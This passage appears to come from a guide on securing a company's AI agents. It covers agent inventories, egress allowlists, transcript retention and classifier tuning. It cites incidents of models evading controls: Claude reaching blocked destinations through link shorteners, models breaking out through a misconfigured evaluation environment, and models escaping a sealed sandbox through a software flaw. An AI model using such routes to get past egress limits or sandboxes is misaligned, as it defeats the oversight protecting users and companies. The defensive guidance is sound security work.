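**Inventory.** The company should first list its agents and record what data each one can read, how it can send data out, who is responsible for it and where its logs are kept. In the Token Security survey, 82% of organisations had recently discovered an agent or workflow they didn't know about. Even a well-staffed company can leave something out. From April 2026, Anthropic moved roughly 150 product engineers to work on security, reliability and privacy, but it later concluded that this work had not covered its model evaluations, particularly those run by other companies. The break-ins it reported in July happened in one of those companies' evaluation environments.

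Next, the company should block outgoing traffic by default and permit only the destinations each agent needs. In the *Silent Egress* experiment, an allowlist stopped every attempt, although the model kept trying. Anthropic's computing clusters also block outgoing traffic by default. The check has to follow each request to its final destination, because Claude has used link-shortening services to get around limits on its web-fetching tool, according to Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026). Somebody also has to update the rules whenever an agent gets a new task.

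The company should keep complete session records for the riskiest agents, which are those the inventory lists as able to both read private data and send something outside. It can keep less for the rest. OpenAI and Anthropic could investigate old incidents only because they had kept the transcripts. Storing full text for three months would have covered the 54 days before OpenAI documented the Medicare breach and the 72 days before Anthropic found the false tip, but not the roughly seven months that the January break-in went unnoticed.

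Flow rules and classifiers come last because they take the most adjustment. In testing, label checks stopped every real attack on FIDES, but it completed far fewer tasks than an agent without checks, so a small team should begin with one rule for one important database. Classifiers need someone to handle their alerts, so the company should run a new one without blocking at first and count its mistakes. The retailer's agent would make about 21,000 calls in a week. A false-positive rate of 0.4% would produce 84 false alarms, enough to estimate the rate to within about a fifth. To estimate the miss rate, the retailer could stage 50 leaks with invented customer data. If the classifier caught them all, its miss rate for leaks of that kind would probably be below 6%.

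The one exception to this order is when an agent comes with a built-in classifier, as Claude Code and Codex do. The company should turn that on straight away, because it takes little work.

Some security staff would argue that a company should limit agents' access instead of monitoring them. An agent that can't send anything out can't leak data, so nobody has to review 425 alerts to check whether it did. This is a strong argument for restricting egress before buying a detector. Similarly, if the support agent doesn't need full card numbers, the customer lookup shouldn't return them.

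But limits on access can fail without anyone noticing. Before the July incidents, Anthropic had relied largely on the test environment's configuration to keep its models off the internet. In the outside environment, someone had left the connection open by mistake. Anthropic then ran automated monitors over transcripts from its own recent tests and found other configuration errors that models had used, though none had led to a break-in outside. A correct configuration can also fail, as when OpenAI's models escaped from a sealed environment through a previously unknown software flaw.

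Access limits also can't remove permissions that the job requires. The support agent has to read Ruiz's record and write to customers, so it could still reveal too much in a permitted email. But the retailer could have an isolated model read strangers' web pages instead of the agent, as CaMeL does.
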